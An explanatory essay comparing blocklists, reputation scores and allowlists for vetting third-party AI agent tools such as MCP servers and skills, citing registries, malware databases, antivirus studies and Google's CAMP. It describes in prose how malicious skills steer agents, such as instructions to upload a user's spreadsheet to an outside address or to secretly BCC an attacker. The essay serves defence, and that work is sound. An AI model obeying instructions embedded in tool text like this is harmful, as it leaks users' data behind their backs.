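# Blocklists, reputation and allowlists for third-party agent tools

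## Third-party agent tools and the three ways to decide which to trust

An AI agent is a system that acts on a user's behalf by calling tools, running code and reading data. The agent's maker builds in some of those tools, but many others come from outside authors whom the user has usually never heard of. Adding one takes about as long as adding a browser extension. A third-party tool is any capability that an agent loads from an outside author, and its publisher is the account or organisation that releases it.

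Blocklists, allowlists and reputation scores are three ways to decide which of these tools may run. A blocklist, or denylist, is a list of tools that may not run, with all others allowed. If an allowlist is used, only the tools on it may run. A reputation score is an estimate of a tool's trustworthiness based on its history and associations, such as its age or its publisher's other releases, and not on its contents.

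### What an agent loads

Third-party tools mostly come as MCP servers, skills or plugins. MCP, the Model Context Protocol, is an open standard that Anthropic introduced in November 2024 for connecting agents to outside tools and data. An MCP server is a program that offers tools through this protocol. With the right server, an assistant can query a database, send an email or deploy code, according to Anthropic's *MCP Subregistry Server*. The protocol's documentation says that the agent's application first connects to the server and requests a list of its tools. For each tool, the server returns a name, a plain-language description and the inputs the tool expects. The language model chooses a tool based on those descriptions, the application passes the call to the server, and the result goes back into the conversation.

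A skill is simpler. It is a folder of written instructions, often with scripts. According to Agent Skills, the site of the open format, an agent loads only each skill's name and description at startup, then reads the full instructions when a task seems to match and follows them, running the scripts if needed. Anthropic's *Equipping agents for the real world with Agent Skills* (2025) describes a skill for PDF files with directions for filling in forms and a short program that extracts a form's fields.

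A plugin is an installable bundle of skills, MCP servers or other extensions. In Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, it can also contain hooks, which are commands that run automatically at set moments in a session.

People find all of these in registries and marketplaces, which are public catalogues that can be very large. SkillsMP, for example, indexes more than four million skill files. To install a plugin in Claude Code, the user types a command with the names of the plugin and its marketplace, reviews a panel that lists what the plugin will add, and chooses whether it applies to every project or only one. Claude Code then downloads the plugin and any other plugins it depends on. Anthropic notes that for a plugin from a local or custom marketplace, the panel can show only a message that the components will be discovered at installation, so the user can't check them there before agreeing.

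### Why the tool acts as the user

An installed tool can usually do whatever the user can. *Securing Claude Code plug-ins* (Kapner, 2026), written for the software company Red Hat, describes a plugin as having full access to the user's terminal, local files and environment variables (settings that often hold passwords and access keys). Anthropic also warns that plugins can run arbitrary code with the user's privileges.

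Operating systems give a program the rights of the account that starts it. When a user starts an agent and the agent starts a server or script, that server or script also gets the user's rights, unless it runs in a sandbox, an isolated environment with fewer rights. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* recommends sandboxes for servers on the user's machine but does not require them. It does require an application that offers one-click installation to show the exact command and get the user's approval first. There is a decent reason to give tools such broad access, since a tool for editing files must be able to reach them.

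A tool can do harm without containing any code. In *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs*, Yang, Ying and colleagues (2026) describe a skill for summarising spreadsheets. Its last written step tells the agent to upload the spreadsheet to an outside address, supposedly for validation. The agent already has permission to read the file and use the network, so the written instruction is enough to make it send the data out.

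### Tools on the user's machine and tools elsewhere

The location of a tool's code greatly affects what anyone can check. A local MCP server runs on the user's computer. A remote one runs on its operator's infrastructure and exchanges messages with the agent over the web (Google Cloud, *MCP server overview*). Skills and plugin files are stored on the user's computer, though a plugin can include a connection to a remote server.

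The user or a reviewer can in principle read a local tool's code, fingerprint it and notice when it changes, but the code runs on the same machine as the user's files. A remote server cannot directly access the user's disk. It receives what the agent sends, plus whatever access the user grants it to accounts such as email. But nobody outside the operator sees its code, and the operator can replace that code at any time without the user installing anything.

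Running a server remotely also gives less protection than it seems to, because the model still reads the server's tool descriptions and results. Shen, Toyoda and Leung (2026), in *MCP-38*, a catalogue of 38 threats to MCP systems, point out that anyone who controls text the model reads can influence the agent without touching application code. For example, a remote server that cannot open a file may still return text that gets the agent to open it.

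### Three rules and three kinds of tool

The terms for these lists are older than agents. In 2015, the *Guide to Application Whitelisting* from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) defined whitelists and blacklists, the former names for allowlists and blocklists. It also defined a graylist, for items not yet known to be benign or malicious. A tool on the graylist is unknown, meaning it is on neither of the other lists.

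| Rule | Known malicious | Known good | Unknown |
|---|---|---|---|
| Blocklist | Refuse | Run | Run |
| Reputation score | Refuse | Run | Run if the score is high enough; otherwise warn, hold for review or refuse |
| Allowlist | Refuse | Run | Refuse until someone reviews and lists it |

The first two columns are the same in every row. The rules differ mainly on the unknown tool, because each list records only one kind of knowledge. Someone enforcing a blocklist can't tell from the list whether a tool is well tested or was uploaded ten minutes ago, since neither kind is on it. An allowlist leaves out both notorious malware and excellent tools that nobody has reviewed yet, so someone enforcing it can't tell those apart either. Reputation is an attempt to sort the unknown tools without reviewing each one. NIST describes reputation services as a way for software to handle new or changed files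 based on their publisher's standing, instead of leaving them for manual processing.

How a rule treats unknown tools might hardly matter in a small office where the tools rarely change. But in a catalogue of millions of skills, most of what a user comes across will be missing from any list that people maintain by hand, so the rule for unknown tools will apply to nearly the whole catalogue.

Whoever writes a list must also choose how each entry identifies a tool. GitHub's *MCP allowlists in enterprise managed settings* (2026) describes three ways employers can identify servers for the Copilot agent: by a remote server's web address, by the exact command that starts a local server, or by name. NIST advises against relying on a filename alone, because an attacker can give a malicious file the name of a harmless one. A cryptographic hash, a fingerprint computed from a file's exact contents,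 is much stricter, but it changes with every update.

Rotation means replacing a tool's name, publisher, files or server address to escape a blocklist. Pinning ties an approval to one exact version of a tool, so a changed version counts as unknown again.

### Who applies the rule

At least five parties can apply one of these rules, and they need not choose the same one.

- The registry. The official MCP Registry, which opened in preview in September 2025, holds information that publishers supply about their own servers. Anyone can report an entry for spam, malicious code or impersonation, and the maintainers can then denylist it and remove it from public access, as the Model Context Protocol project announced at the launch. That is a blocklist, which works after publication.
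- The marketplace. Marketplaces can draw on a registry and add criteria of their own. Some run scanners, software that inspects a tool and returns a verdict on whether it is malicious. ClawHub, the public skill hub for the agent OpenClaw, uses three of them, while Yang and colleagues found none at SkillsMP.
- The maker of the agent. Cursor, which makes a coding agent, reviews every plugin and every update by hand before listing it, according to Cursor's *Marketplace security*. Anthropic curates one marketplace for Claude Code and puts submissions to a second through automated screening, but users may add any other marketplace they like. Kapner complains that the plugin marketplace has no centralised vetting, which seems fair for those others and too strong for Anthropic's own two.
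- The employer. Anthropic's *Control MCP server access for your organization* gives administrators a range of settings that runs from no servers at all, through an approved catalogue, to a denylist with everything else allowed. Out of the box there is no restriction. The British environment department is at the cautious end: in Defra's *Claude Code plugin marketplace* it tells staff that plugins do not yet have approval for delivery work.
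- The user, who decides by default when nobody else does. Anthropic's advice is to install skills only from trusted sources and to audit anything from a less trusted one by reading its files, which few people will do every time.

Each check in this chain can block a server that earlier checks let through. A registry may accept a server because nobody has reported it, and an employer may then block it because it isn't on the company's allowlist. But an employer's rule covers only its own staff, and somebody using an agent at home may have only the registry's blocklist and their own judgement.

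### Four ways a tool can be hostile

Some tools are malicious from the start. Their authors write them to steal credentials or run an attacker's commands, and disguise them as something useful. In the ClawHavoc campaign, which came to light in February 2026, attackers put hundreds of such skills on ClawHub.

An impostor copies the name or appearance of a tool that people already trust. Shen and colleagues trace this risk to the protocol itself, which does not require a server to prove its identity cryptographically, so trust rests on a web address or a file path. The official registry partly addresses this by using the domain name system to check that a publisher controls the internet domain it publishes under (Model Context Protocol documentation). This check confirms who owns a name but not whether the owner is honest.

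An author can also deliberately turn a tool malicious after a period of good behaviour in which it gains users and approvals. Security researchers call this a rug pull, and the usual example is the email server postmark-mcp. In other cases, an attacker takes over an honest author's tool by stealing the publisher's account, tampering with a component the tool depends on, or breaking into the service that hosts it. A breach in October 2025 at Smithery, a registry that also hosts servers, exposed control of more than 3,000 hosted applications, according to the anonymous guide mcpowered.

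The choice of rule depends partly on when the attack happens. A careful review before installation may catch an impostor or a tool that is malicious from the start, but it cannot catch a later rug pull or takeover, because the tool is not yet malicious when it is reviewed.

Tools that are merely insecure are a different problem, because their developers mean no harm but have left a flaw that others can exploit. Shen and colleagues cite mcp-remote, a legitimate package for connecting to remote servers, which had a flaw that let a malicious server run commands on the user's machine by supplying a specially crafted web address. Such a flaw should be repaired, since blocking the tool permanently would punish the wrong party.

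Hostile tools are hard to tell from carelessly made ones. Yang and colleagues classify skills by intent as well as harm. They call a skill "risky" if it has a legitimate purpose but potentially harmful behaviour, "suspicious" if they cannot determine its intent, and "malicious" only if there is evidence of intent to compromise the user. Of 157 skills that earlier researchers had labelled malicious, they confirmed 95 as malicious by this test.

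### Measuring a screening rule

Four quantities recur in arguments about which third-party tools to trust. Recall is the share of malicious tools that a scanner flags. The false-positive rate is the share of harmless tools that it flags. The base rate is the share of all tools that are malicious. The exposure window is the time between a malicious tool's release and when users are protected from it.

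A hypothetical catalogue of 100,000 skills, 100 of them malicious, has a base rate of 0.1%. This is roughly the rate the earlier researchers found, with 95 confirmed malicious skills among the 98,380 they searched. It is probably an underestimate, because it counts only the malicious skills they found. The example assumes a scanner with a recall of 95.1% and a false-positive rate of 17.8%, the figures Yang and colleagues report for the best performer among the scanners that public hubs have adopted.

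The scanner flags 95 of the 100 malicious skills, but it also flags about 17,800 of the 99,900 harmless ones, so only about one warning in 190 points to a malicious skill. This is mostly because malicious skills are so rare. If one skill in a hundred were malicious, about one in 20 of the same scanner's warnings would be correct.

Suppose one of the 5 missed skills gains 50 new users a day, and the marketplace removes it after four days, when somebody complains. For people who had not yet installed it, the exposure window was four days. The 200 who had installed it are still exposed until something disables the copy on their machines, because delisting a skill does not delete it. A cooldown is a rule that a new release may not be installed until it has been public for a set time. It is meant to ensure that the exposure window ends before the first installation. A seven-day cooldown would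 have protected all 200 users, provided somebody not bound by the rule had still tried the skill and complained.

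## The case for allowing tools unless they are known to be malicious

A blocklist allows tools that nobody has examined to run. There is a good argument for this approach, which the official MCP Registry follows.

The argument starts from how rare malicious tools seem to be. In *Do Not Mention This to the User*, Liu, Chen and colleagues (2026) searched 98,380 agent skills and confirmed 157 as malicious, or 0.16%, the same 157 that Yang and colleagues later rechecked. If the other skills are harmless, a rule that blocked every skill until it was reviewed would hold back more than 600 harmless skills for each malicious one.

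Open publication also lets anyone contribute. Somebody who writes a server for an obscure database doesn't have to persuade a reviewer to look at it, and a catalogue with hardly any staff can still list it. To block a tool, somebody has to point to something it does, such as sending passwords to a stranger, and the publisher can dispute that claim, whereas a publisher waiting for review has no specific claim to dispute.

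Findings that a tool is malicious are also easy to share. Once one researcher has shown that a package steals credentials, everyone can block it, including people who could not have worked that out from the code. Approvals are harder to share because they depend more on the user. A hospital and a games studio may reasonably disagree about whether to allow a tool that uploads files, but neither wants one that steals passwords.

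The weakness of this approach is that somebody has to discover a malicious tool before it can be blocked, often after other people have installed it. The longer that takes, the more harm the tool can do.

### Moderation at the MCP Registry

The MCP Registry holds descriptions of servers but not their code. A publisher submits a name, a description and a pointer to the server, either at a remote address or in a package registry such as npm (for JavaScript) or PyPI (for Python).

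Before accepting an entry, the Model Context Protocol registry checks that the publisher controls the namespace, which is the first part of the server's name. To publish io.github.alice/weather-server, someone must log in to GitHub as alice. To publish under com.example, they must put a cryptographic key in the domain's DNS records or in a file on its website. Only owners of a GitHub organisation can now publish under its namespace. Previously, any member could do so and could overwrite the organisation's servers.

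The registry does not scan a server's code for malware. It leaves that to the package registries and to the marketplaces that copy its entries.

Under Model Context Protocol's moderation policy, the maintainers remove illegal content, malware, spam and servers that don't work. They keep adult content and servers that are buggy, duplicate others or have security vulnerabilities. Keeping vulnerable servers fits the distinction between insecure and hostile tools, but attackers can still use the flaws to break into users' machines.

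The policy also warns users of the data to "assume minimal-to-no moderation". The registry is a community project with little capacity for moderation, and some entries that break its rules may not have been removed yet. Applications such as coding agents are meant to go through a marketplace, which can add its own checks, instead of reading the registry directly.

This division of labour is sensible if the others do their part. But a remote server has no package for npm or PyPI to scan, so only the marketplaces are left to check it.

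When the maintainers remove a server, they set its status to "deleted" and usually leave its entry readable, so a marketplace that has already copied the entry can see that the server was withdrawn. Under Model Context Protocol, marketplaces are expected to fetch updates about once an hour, but they can't be forced to drop a deleted server. A publisher who thinks the removal was a mistake can appeal by opening an issue on GitHub.

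### From a report to a block

A block takes several steps, and different organisations often carry them out. The record for postmark-mcp, the usual example of a rug pull, is a convenient specimen. It is in OSV, a public database of software vulnerabilities and malicious packages. These are the main fields of OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025):

| Field | Content |
|---|---|
| Ecosystem | npm |
| Package | postmark-mcp |
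| Affected versions | 1.0.16 onwards |
| Source | google-open-source-security |
| Published | 26 September 2025, 04:14 UTC |
| Reason | Turned malicious in version 1.0.16; sends out email data through BCC |

Somebody notices the tool and **reports** it. The OSV record comes from a repository of malicious packages run by the Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF). The repository opened in 2023 with more than 15,000 reports and accepts new ones from volunteers and automated detection systems. Users of the MCP Registry report a server by opening an issue.

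**Confirmation.** According to OpenSSF's *How to contribute*, every submitted report needs a review, even one from a member of the project. OpenSSF notes that people can also amend or dispute reports after publication, and the repository has a folder for reports that turned out to be wrong. On the skill hub ClawHub, moderators can hold a listing while they resolve a high-risk case and lift the hold if it was a false positive, according to OpenClaw.

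The people who write a blocklist entry decide exactly what it blocks. The entry for postmark-mcp identifies the package by name and covers version 1.0.16 and every later release, but not the earlier, benign versions.

A blocklist entry has to reach the people it is meant to protect. Any program can send OSV a package's name and version and get back the matching records. GitHub also copies OpenSSF's reports into its own advisory database, which covers eight package ecosystems. GitHub's *How we took malware advisories beyond npm* gives some support to the argument for sharing reports. More than half of the new npm reports reaching OpenSSF's repository each month had come from GitHub, but the rest were new to GitHub.

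GitHub publishes these malware advisories without a person reading each one, reasoning that a review queue of several days would mostly help the attacker. But a shared list also spreads mistakes. A false report against a popular package would reach everyone who relies on the list, and an attacker who broke into the source could submit a whole batch of false reports. GitHub therefore caps the number of advisories in each import. If an import exceeds the cap, GitHub publishes none of it and alerts its staff. Staff can also trace every advisory to the upstream change that produced it and undo a bad batch in one step.

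**Enforcement.** Finally, a program on the user's side has to act on the entry. GitHub's Dependabot checks a software project's packages, including existing ones, against the advisory database. It only sends an alert, and only if the project's owner has turned on malware alerts. OSV-Scanner, a free program that developers can run on each proposed code change, is stricter. The check fails if the change adds a known malicious package, according to *Detecting Malicious Packages using the OSV API* (Douglas, 2026). Douglas works for Cloudsmith, which sells package management software.

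Both programs were made for software projects with a list of dependencies. A person who tells a desktop agent to start an npm server with a single command may have no such list. Unless the agent's application looks up the package in OSV, that person is protected only if npm has removed it. Coverage is also incomplete, because GitHub's eight ecosystems are all for conventional software packages. They include an MCP server published on npm, but not a remote server with no package or a skill that exists only as a folder on a skill hub.

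### What an attacker must change

Attackers can evade each kind of identifier in a different way. Broader identifiers are harder to evade, but they are also more likely to block harmless tools.

| The list identifies the tool by | To escape, the attacker must change | The block may also hit |
|---|---|---|
| File hash | One byte of the file | Nothing else |
| Name and version range | The name, if the range has no end; otherwise the version number | Later honest versions, until somebody amends the entry |
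| Publisher | The account or domain used to publish | Honest tools from the same publisher |
| Domain or server address | The address | Honest tools at the same domain |

A file hash is the easiest kind of blocklist entry to evade. *CloudAV*, a 2008 study of antivirus software by Oberheide, Cooke and Jahanian, points out that changing a single byte is enough. An attacker could add a space to a malicious skill's instructions, and its hash would no longer match the one on the list.

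Blocking a malicious tool by name sets the attacker back. The publisher of postmark-mcp can upload the same code under another name in a few minutes, but the new package starts without the users that the old one gained by behaving well. An impostor relies heavily on the name, since users install the tool because they recognise it. But blocking by name is too broad when an attacker has taken over an honest package. Attackers compromised two versions of axios, a popular JavaScript library, and OSV's record covers only those versions. Blocking the name would also have cut developers off from all the good releases.

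Blocking a publisher removes everything the account has released, but the attacker can open another account. On the MCP Registry, that takes a new GitHub login or a new domain. Blocking also penalizes honest authors whose accounts were stolen.

For a remote server, the list-keeper has only a name, a publisher and an address to go by, with no files to examine. *CAMP*, a 2013 paper by Abu Rajab, Ballard and colleagues at Google, describes the problem with relying on addresses in lists of websites that distribute malware. According to the paper, some services let an attacker move to new domains very cheaply, and an attacker who moves faster than the list updates will stay ahead of it. The team found that such lists work much better for honest websites that an attacker has compromised, because those tend to keep the same address.

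### The 157 malicious skills

The argument depends on malicious tools being rare and on catalogues removing them when told, and Liu and colleagues studied both. In January 2026 they copied the listings of two community registries, skills.rest and SkillsMP, which find skills by crawling public GitHub repositories. They searched each skill for 14 suspicious patterns, such as code that collects passwords, and used a language model to look for manipulative instructions. This left 4,287 possibly malicious skills.

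They then ran every candidate in a sandbox stocked with fake credentials and recorded what it did. They found suspicious behaviour in 762 of them. Two researchers independently examined each of these, and counted a skill as malicious only if both thought it was. Most of the 605 not counted as malicious were ordinary tools that do sensitive things, such as password managers and programs for testing a network's security.

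The registries had removed or delisted 147 of the 157 skills by the time the team submitted the paper, and the other ten later. So registries that do no vetting of their own will still act on a good report. But delisting may achieve less than it appears to, because these registries are indexes, and removing a skill from one doesn't delete the GitHub repository that holds its files.

One actor had made 85 of the 157 skills, or 54.1%. Each was presented as a tool for a different brand, and all of them contained the same 26 lines of text assuring users that their credentials were safe, while the skill downloaded and ran code from the attacker's server. A blocklist suits this case well if it uses the right identifier. Blocking the skills by name would take 85 entries, but blocking the publisher would take one. A rule matching the shared lines would also take one, and it would still work if the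 attacker opened a new account. Liu and colleagues think such a check at submission could have stopped the whole campaign with trivial effort.

Matching on shared text can block legitimate tools, though. Another of the 157 was a copy of a legitimate skill for making presentations, with three lines added that caused the agent to upload the user's files. The two texts were 98.3% alike, so a rule that blocked anything resembling the malicious version would have blocked the original too.

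The team defines its count of 157 malicious skills as a minimum. They did not run the 94,093 skills that matched no pattern, and each sandbox run lasted at most 60 seconds. To estimate what they had missed, two researchers read 413 of the 4,130 unconfirmed candidates. About 2% were attacks that only work over several sessions, which would mean about 78 such attacks among all 4,130.

Another 93% of the sample contained triggers that had not fired, such as code that waits for a certain date or a certain kind of machine. An appendix to the paper calls these "dormant malware". If that were right, the two registries would have held about 4,000 malicious skills, or one in 25, and the argument from rarity would be much weaker. The label is probably too strong, because the 605 rejected skills had looked worse in the sandbox and most of them turned out to be ordinary tools. The true number of malicious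 skills is unknown.

The count may also be too high. Yang and colleagues applied a stricter test of intent and confirmed only 95 of the 157. Liu and colleagues treat the removal of all 157 as independent proof that their labels were right, but the registries also removed the 62 that Yang and colleagues did not confirm. This suggests that the registries respond to reports, but it is rather weak evidence that they check them.

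Liu and colleagues do not think removing malicious skills afterwards is enough. They say users had no way to tell these skills from the rest for about three months before the report. When the team searched the registries again later in 2026, they found 12.6 times as many skills, so a list based on the January search would have covered only a small part of the catalogue.

### What happened to antivirus signatures

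Antivirus software has relied on blocklists for decades. In the classic method, a company obtains a malicious program and derives a signature, a pattern that recurs in copies of the program. It sends the signature to its customers, whose software checks each file against the list of signatures. Unlike a hash, one signature can match many variants of the same program. The 26 lines shared by the brand-impersonating skills would make a good signature.

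Attackers responded by repackaging their programs. They compress or encrypt a program, or make it rewrite its own code in each copy, so that it does the same thing but no longer matches the pattern. They can also buy the antivirus product, and Abu Rajab and colleagues describe malware authors who test their work against it and keep repackaging until it raises no alarm.

Oberheide and colleagues collected 7,220 pieces of malware over a year ending in November 2007, updated ten antivirus products the day after collection ended, and counted what each one caught. The products detected between 57.5% and 89.2% of the malware from the last three months, but only 39.6% to 78.5% of the malware from the last week. Abu Rajab and colleagues later summarised the study as showing that major products caught 35% to 70% of recent malware, a little lower than the figures in the study's table. By either account,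 the best product missed more than a fifth of the newest malware.

Some of the same study's results favour shared lists. A typical single product caught 83% of the year's malware, while the team's own system, which combined ten products with two tools that analyse behaviour, caught 98%. The team also proposed that organisations record which machines have opened which files, so that they can still find the machines that need cleaning when a verdict arrives weeks late.

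Antivirus companies kept their signatures and added other defences. AV-Comparatives' *Malware Protection Test* (2026) shows roughly what each contributes. In March 2026 the independent laboratory tested 20 consumer products on 10,000 pieces of malware. Without an internet connection, scanning caught 91.2% on average. Offline scanning is the test's closest equivalent to a plain signature list, though it also includes some guessing from a file's general features. With a connection, the products could also use online data from their makers, such as newer signatures and reputation scores, and the average rose to 96.8%.

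The laboratory then ran whatever the scans had missed, so that the products could stop programs that behaved like malware. That brought average protection to 99.79%. One product, Panda, caught only 56.1% offline but reached 99.17% by the end. It also raised 54 false alarms on clean files, the most of any product, compared with an average of 14.

These figures can't be compared with the ones from 2008 to measure how much detection has improved. AV-Comparatives stopped collecting samples about a month before the test, so the companies had weeks to respond to even the newest ones. The products of 2007 were worst at detecting malware less than a week old.

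Looking up a package in OSV corresponds only to the first of these defences, the list. A list of signatures may also do worse on skills than on programs. Of the 632 harmful elements that Liu and colleagues labelled in the 157 skills, 84.2% were in the written instructions. An attacker can reword a paragraph in a minute, or have a language model produce a hundred versions of it, and an agent will follow any of them.

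Watching what a tool does may also help less than it does with ordinary malware. One of the 157 was an email skill with instructions for the agent to add the attacker's address to the BCC field and not mention it to the user. Postmark-mcp did much the same in code. In both cases, monitoring software on the machine would have recorded an email tool sending an email, which is normal behavior for such a tool.

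## The case for judging unknown tools by reputation

A blocklist lets an unknown tool run and an allowlist refuses it, in both cases without anyone examining the tool. People who favour reputation scores think this ignores useful evidence, such as whether the publisher has released anything else, how long the tool has been public, how many users it has, and whether it shares a server with tools already on a blocklist.

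This evidence is harder to change than a file. An attacker can reword a skill in a minute but cannot change when it was first published. Abu Rajab and colleagues point out that a harmless program can stay at one address, while malware distributors keep changing their files and addresses to escape blocklists. If so, an unfamiliar file at an unfamiliar address is somewhat suspicious, whatever it contains.

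### How Google scored downloads

The model case is CAMP (Content-Agnostic Malware Protection), which Google built into its Chrome browser to protect people downloading Windows programs. The idea predates Google's 2013 description of it. Aycock (2013), in *Greetz from academe*, recalls researchers from the antivirus company Symantec presenting a reputation system in 2009, and Microsoft already had SmartScreen. But Google published both a detailed design and results from a very large number of users.

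CAMP combines all three rules. When someone downloads a program, Chrome goes through these steps:

1. It compares the download's address with Safe Browsing, Google's blocklist of malicious sites, and warns the user if there is a match.
2. It compares the website and the program's signer with an allowlist. To get onto this list, a site or signer must have gone at least 90 days without Google seeing any sign of malice from it.
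3. If neither list settles the matter, Chrome sends Google a description of the download. This includes its web address, the server's IP address, any pages that redirected the user there, and the file's size, hash and digital signature. The file itself stays on the user's machine. Google's server answers "benign", "malicious" or "unknown".

About 70% of downloads never reached the third step, because they matched the allowlist or were a type of file that Chrome did not consider risky. The first version of the allowlist had 243 domains and covered about 47% of the downloads that Chrome needed to check. The team estimated that 1,000 domains would cover 73%, and 1,000 signers about 85%. The reputation score was for the many smaller publishers.

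The score is based on simple counts. If CAMP has recorded ten downloads from an IP address and six were malicious, the record for that address is six out of ten. CAMP keeps such records for websites, domains and IP addresses, over periods from one day to about three months. It also keeps them for blocks of neighbouring IP addresses, so a new server starts with a bad record if many downloads from its block were malicious.

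A few rules then compare the counts with thresholds. One rule might flag a download if more than a certain share of the files from its site were malicious, and any single rule can trigger a warning. The team preferred these rules to a machine-learning model because staff could read them and work out what caused a false alarm. Each rule was weak by itself. For example, at a threshold strict enough for 95% of its warnings to be correct, a rule based on a site's record caught less than a fifth of the malware. But the rules mostly caught different downloads, so together they caught much more.

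Abu Rajab and colleagues measured the system from February to July 2012, when about 200 million people were using it. It handled 8 to 10 million requests a day and labelled 200,000 to 300,000 of them malicious. It caught about five million malware downloads a month that Safe Browsing had missed.

The team reports that CAMP was 98.6% accurate when judged against Google's own analysis, which ran programs in a virtual machine and watched what they did. High accuracy is easy to reach here because most downloads are harmless. CAMP flagged only about 2% to 4% of requests, so a system that approved everything would have been right more than nine times in ten. Recall was about 70%, so CAMP missed about three in ten malicious downloads. The false-positive rate was mostly between 1% and 2%. A rate of 2% falls to 0.6% if the downloads that Chrome approved locally are included.

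At nine million requests a day, even a 1% rate of mistaken warnings would produce 90,000 of them. Some of the warnings counted as mistaken were probably correct, because Google had tuned its analysis to avoid calling harmless programs malicious, which made it miss some malware. The team sent 1,100 programs that the analysis had called clean to VirusTotal, a service that runs dozens of antivirus products. Ten days later, 12% of those programs were flagged by at least a fifth of the products, although many were adware, which Google had deliberately left out.

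CAMP's verdicts also often differed from those of antivirus products. Of about 8,400 programs that CAMP labelled malicious, the best of four products flagged 25% on the same day, and all four together flagged less than 40%. The team argues that this gap reflects antivirus products' poor detection of new malware, which Oberheide and colleagues had also found, rather than false alarms by CAMP, whose false-positive rate was low. That is probably right, but the products were at a disadvantage because they had no network access and so could not use their makers' online data.

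### Programs with no history

CAMP's server returned "unknown" if Google had never analysed the file, no trusted signer had signed it, and neither the file nor its site was popular. Chrome then warned the user that the file was not commonly downloaded and offered to delete it.

A campaign in February 2012 shows why judging by reputation was useful. The attackers distributed a fake antivirus program that made the computer unusable until the owner paid a registration fee. In about two weeks they used more than 13,000 domains, half of which lasted less than seven minutes, and they changed the file roughly every ten minutes. When the team submitted a sample to VirusTotal, only one of 40 antivirus products recognised it. To keep up, a blocklist's maintainers would have had to find, analyse and publish each new domain within minutes. Google had no sample at first, but Chrome still warned users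 because the program had no history.

Abu Rajab and colleagues conclude that an "unknown" verdict is a very strong sign of malware. Their evidence is decent for busy sites but weak for small ones, where most honest newcomers would be. They followed sites with unknown programs for ten days and found that 74% no longer appeared in users' requests the next day, presumably because the attackers had moved on. But a hobbyist's site that gets one download a week would disappear from the requests too. Google's analysis later found malware on only 0.02% of the sites and cleared 8%. The team checked the busiest of the cleared sites by hand and found that almost all of them hosted dangerous downloads.

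Google and Microsoft still judge downloads by reputation. In 2024 Google split Chrome's warnings into "suspicious", for files whose risk is uncertain, and "dangerous". Windows 11 has a stricter feature, Smart App Control, which blocks programs without a valid signature unless Microsoft's cloud service predicts that they are safe.

Such a system would have less evidence for judging agent tools. The fake antivirus campaign used only five IP addresses, which tied its thousands of domains together. Skills are often hosted on GitHub, where honest and malicious publishers share the same domain and servers. Google could also watch 200 million people through one browser, while people who install skills use many different agents and marketplaces. In a catalogue of four million skills, most skills probably have few users. If a marketplace warned about every skill with few users, people would soon learn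 to ignore the warning.

### Trust scores for agent tools

Several researchers have proposed reputation scores for agent tools. *Securing GenAI Multi-Agent Systems Against Tool Squatting* (Narajala, Huang and Habler, 2025) describes a company registry that gives each tool a score, for example from 0 to 100. The score depends on whether the tool is up to date, how severe the known flaws in its components are, how promptly its vendor has fixed past flaws, and whether anyone seems to be exploiting the tool. Agents can limit their searches to tools above a minimum score. The company can also set a minimum for a particular tool. If the tool's score falls below that minimum, the registry stops issuing the short-lived credentials that agents need to call it.

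The paper gives no formula or weights for the score and tests nothing. The score also would not help much with unknown tools, since an administrator must approve a tool before it gets one. The inputs mostly measure whether a tool is insecure, not whether it is hostile. The developer of postmark-mcp could have used the latest components, with no known flaws, and still copied every user's email.

*Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (2026) does give a formula, which is part of an open-source program called SkillFortify. It combines four signals, each between 0 and 1:

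| Signal | Weight | Scores 0 | Scores 1 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Provenance | 0.3 | Anonymous author, no signature | Verified organisation, signed, with a reproducible build |
| Behaviour | 0.3 | Scanner finds critical violations | Scanner finds nothing |
| Community | 0.2 | New, with no users | Mature and widely used, with no reported problems |
| History | 0.2 | Past vulnerabilities or incidents | Clean record |

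The trust score is the weighted sum. If a skill depends on other skills, SkillFortify multiplies its score by their lowest score, so a skill at 0.8 whose weakest dependency is at 0.6 gets 0.48. The final score falls into one of four levels: "unsigned" below 0.25, "signed" from 0.25, "community verified" from 0.5 and "formally verified" from 0.75.

Part of this score, the behaviour signal, comes from scanning the skill's contents, and a clean scan can make up for a missing reputation. A skill that an anonymous author uploaded this morning scores 0 for provenance and 0 for community. If the scanner finds nothing, the skill scores 1 for behaviour, and if an empty record counts as a clean one, it also scores 1 for history. The weighted total is 0.3 + 0.2 = 0.5, which makes the skill "community verified" before anyone has used it. The paper suggests that a company could require this level for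 the skills it uses in production.

The score also decays by about 1% a day until the next update, because neglected software tends to accumulate flaws. At that rate it halves every 69 days. A perfect skill that needs no changes would drop to the "unsigned" level after 139 days, although its signature would still be valid. An update restores the score unless the scanner finds something wrong, so a rug pull, which arrives as an update, would also restore it if the scanner missed the malicious change.

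A company could fix some of this by requiring a minimum for each signal instead of adding the signals up, but it would still have to decide how to treat a tool with no record. *Capability Advertisement as a Market for Lemons* (2026) proposes attaching reputation records to MCP tools and keeping them in a public log that nobody can rewrite. It suggests a cautious default for tools without a record. It does not test this in practice, but there is a good theoretical reason for the caution.

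### Why newcomers have to pay

A bad reputation punishes a publisher only if the publisher can't switch to a new name. In *The Social Cost of Cheap Pseudonyms*, Friedman and Resnick (2001) study this problem with a game in which players meet in random pairs. If both cooperate, each gains 1. If only one cheats, the cheater gains 2 and the other player loses 1. If both cheat, neither gains anything. Everyone can look up each name's past behavior.

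When names are permanent, players can cheat anyone who cheated in the previous round, and this threat keeps nearly everyone cooperating. But a cheat who can change names freely can return as a newcomer, and escapes punishment if the others treat newcomers well.

Cooperation can survive if newcomers tolerate being cheated sometimes by established players, because starting again under a new name then puts a player at a disadvantage. Friedman and Resnick prove that no stable arrangement does substantially better than this in a large population where a few players make mistakes or enjoy causing trouble. If a share α of the players leaves and is replaced each round, the best average payoff is 1 − α/(2 − α), compared with 1 when names are permanent. With a tenth of the players leaving each round, the loss is about 5%.

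Judging unknown tools by reputation puts newcomers at a disadvantage, although most have done nothing wrong. For example, Chrome warns users about uncommon downloads, and a marketplace may rank newcomers low in its search results.

One person can also use many names at once, which security researchers call a Sybil attack. An attacker can escape a bad reputation by taking a new name, or build a good one by using a hundred names to install, star and recommend a tool. Douceur's *The Sybil Attack* shows that without a central authority to vouch for identities, these attacks are always possible except under unrealistic assumptions, such as that everyone has similar computing resources. GitHub and the marketplaces could act as that authority, but checking that someone controls an account, as the MCP Registry does, doesn't establish that they have only one.

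### A worked example

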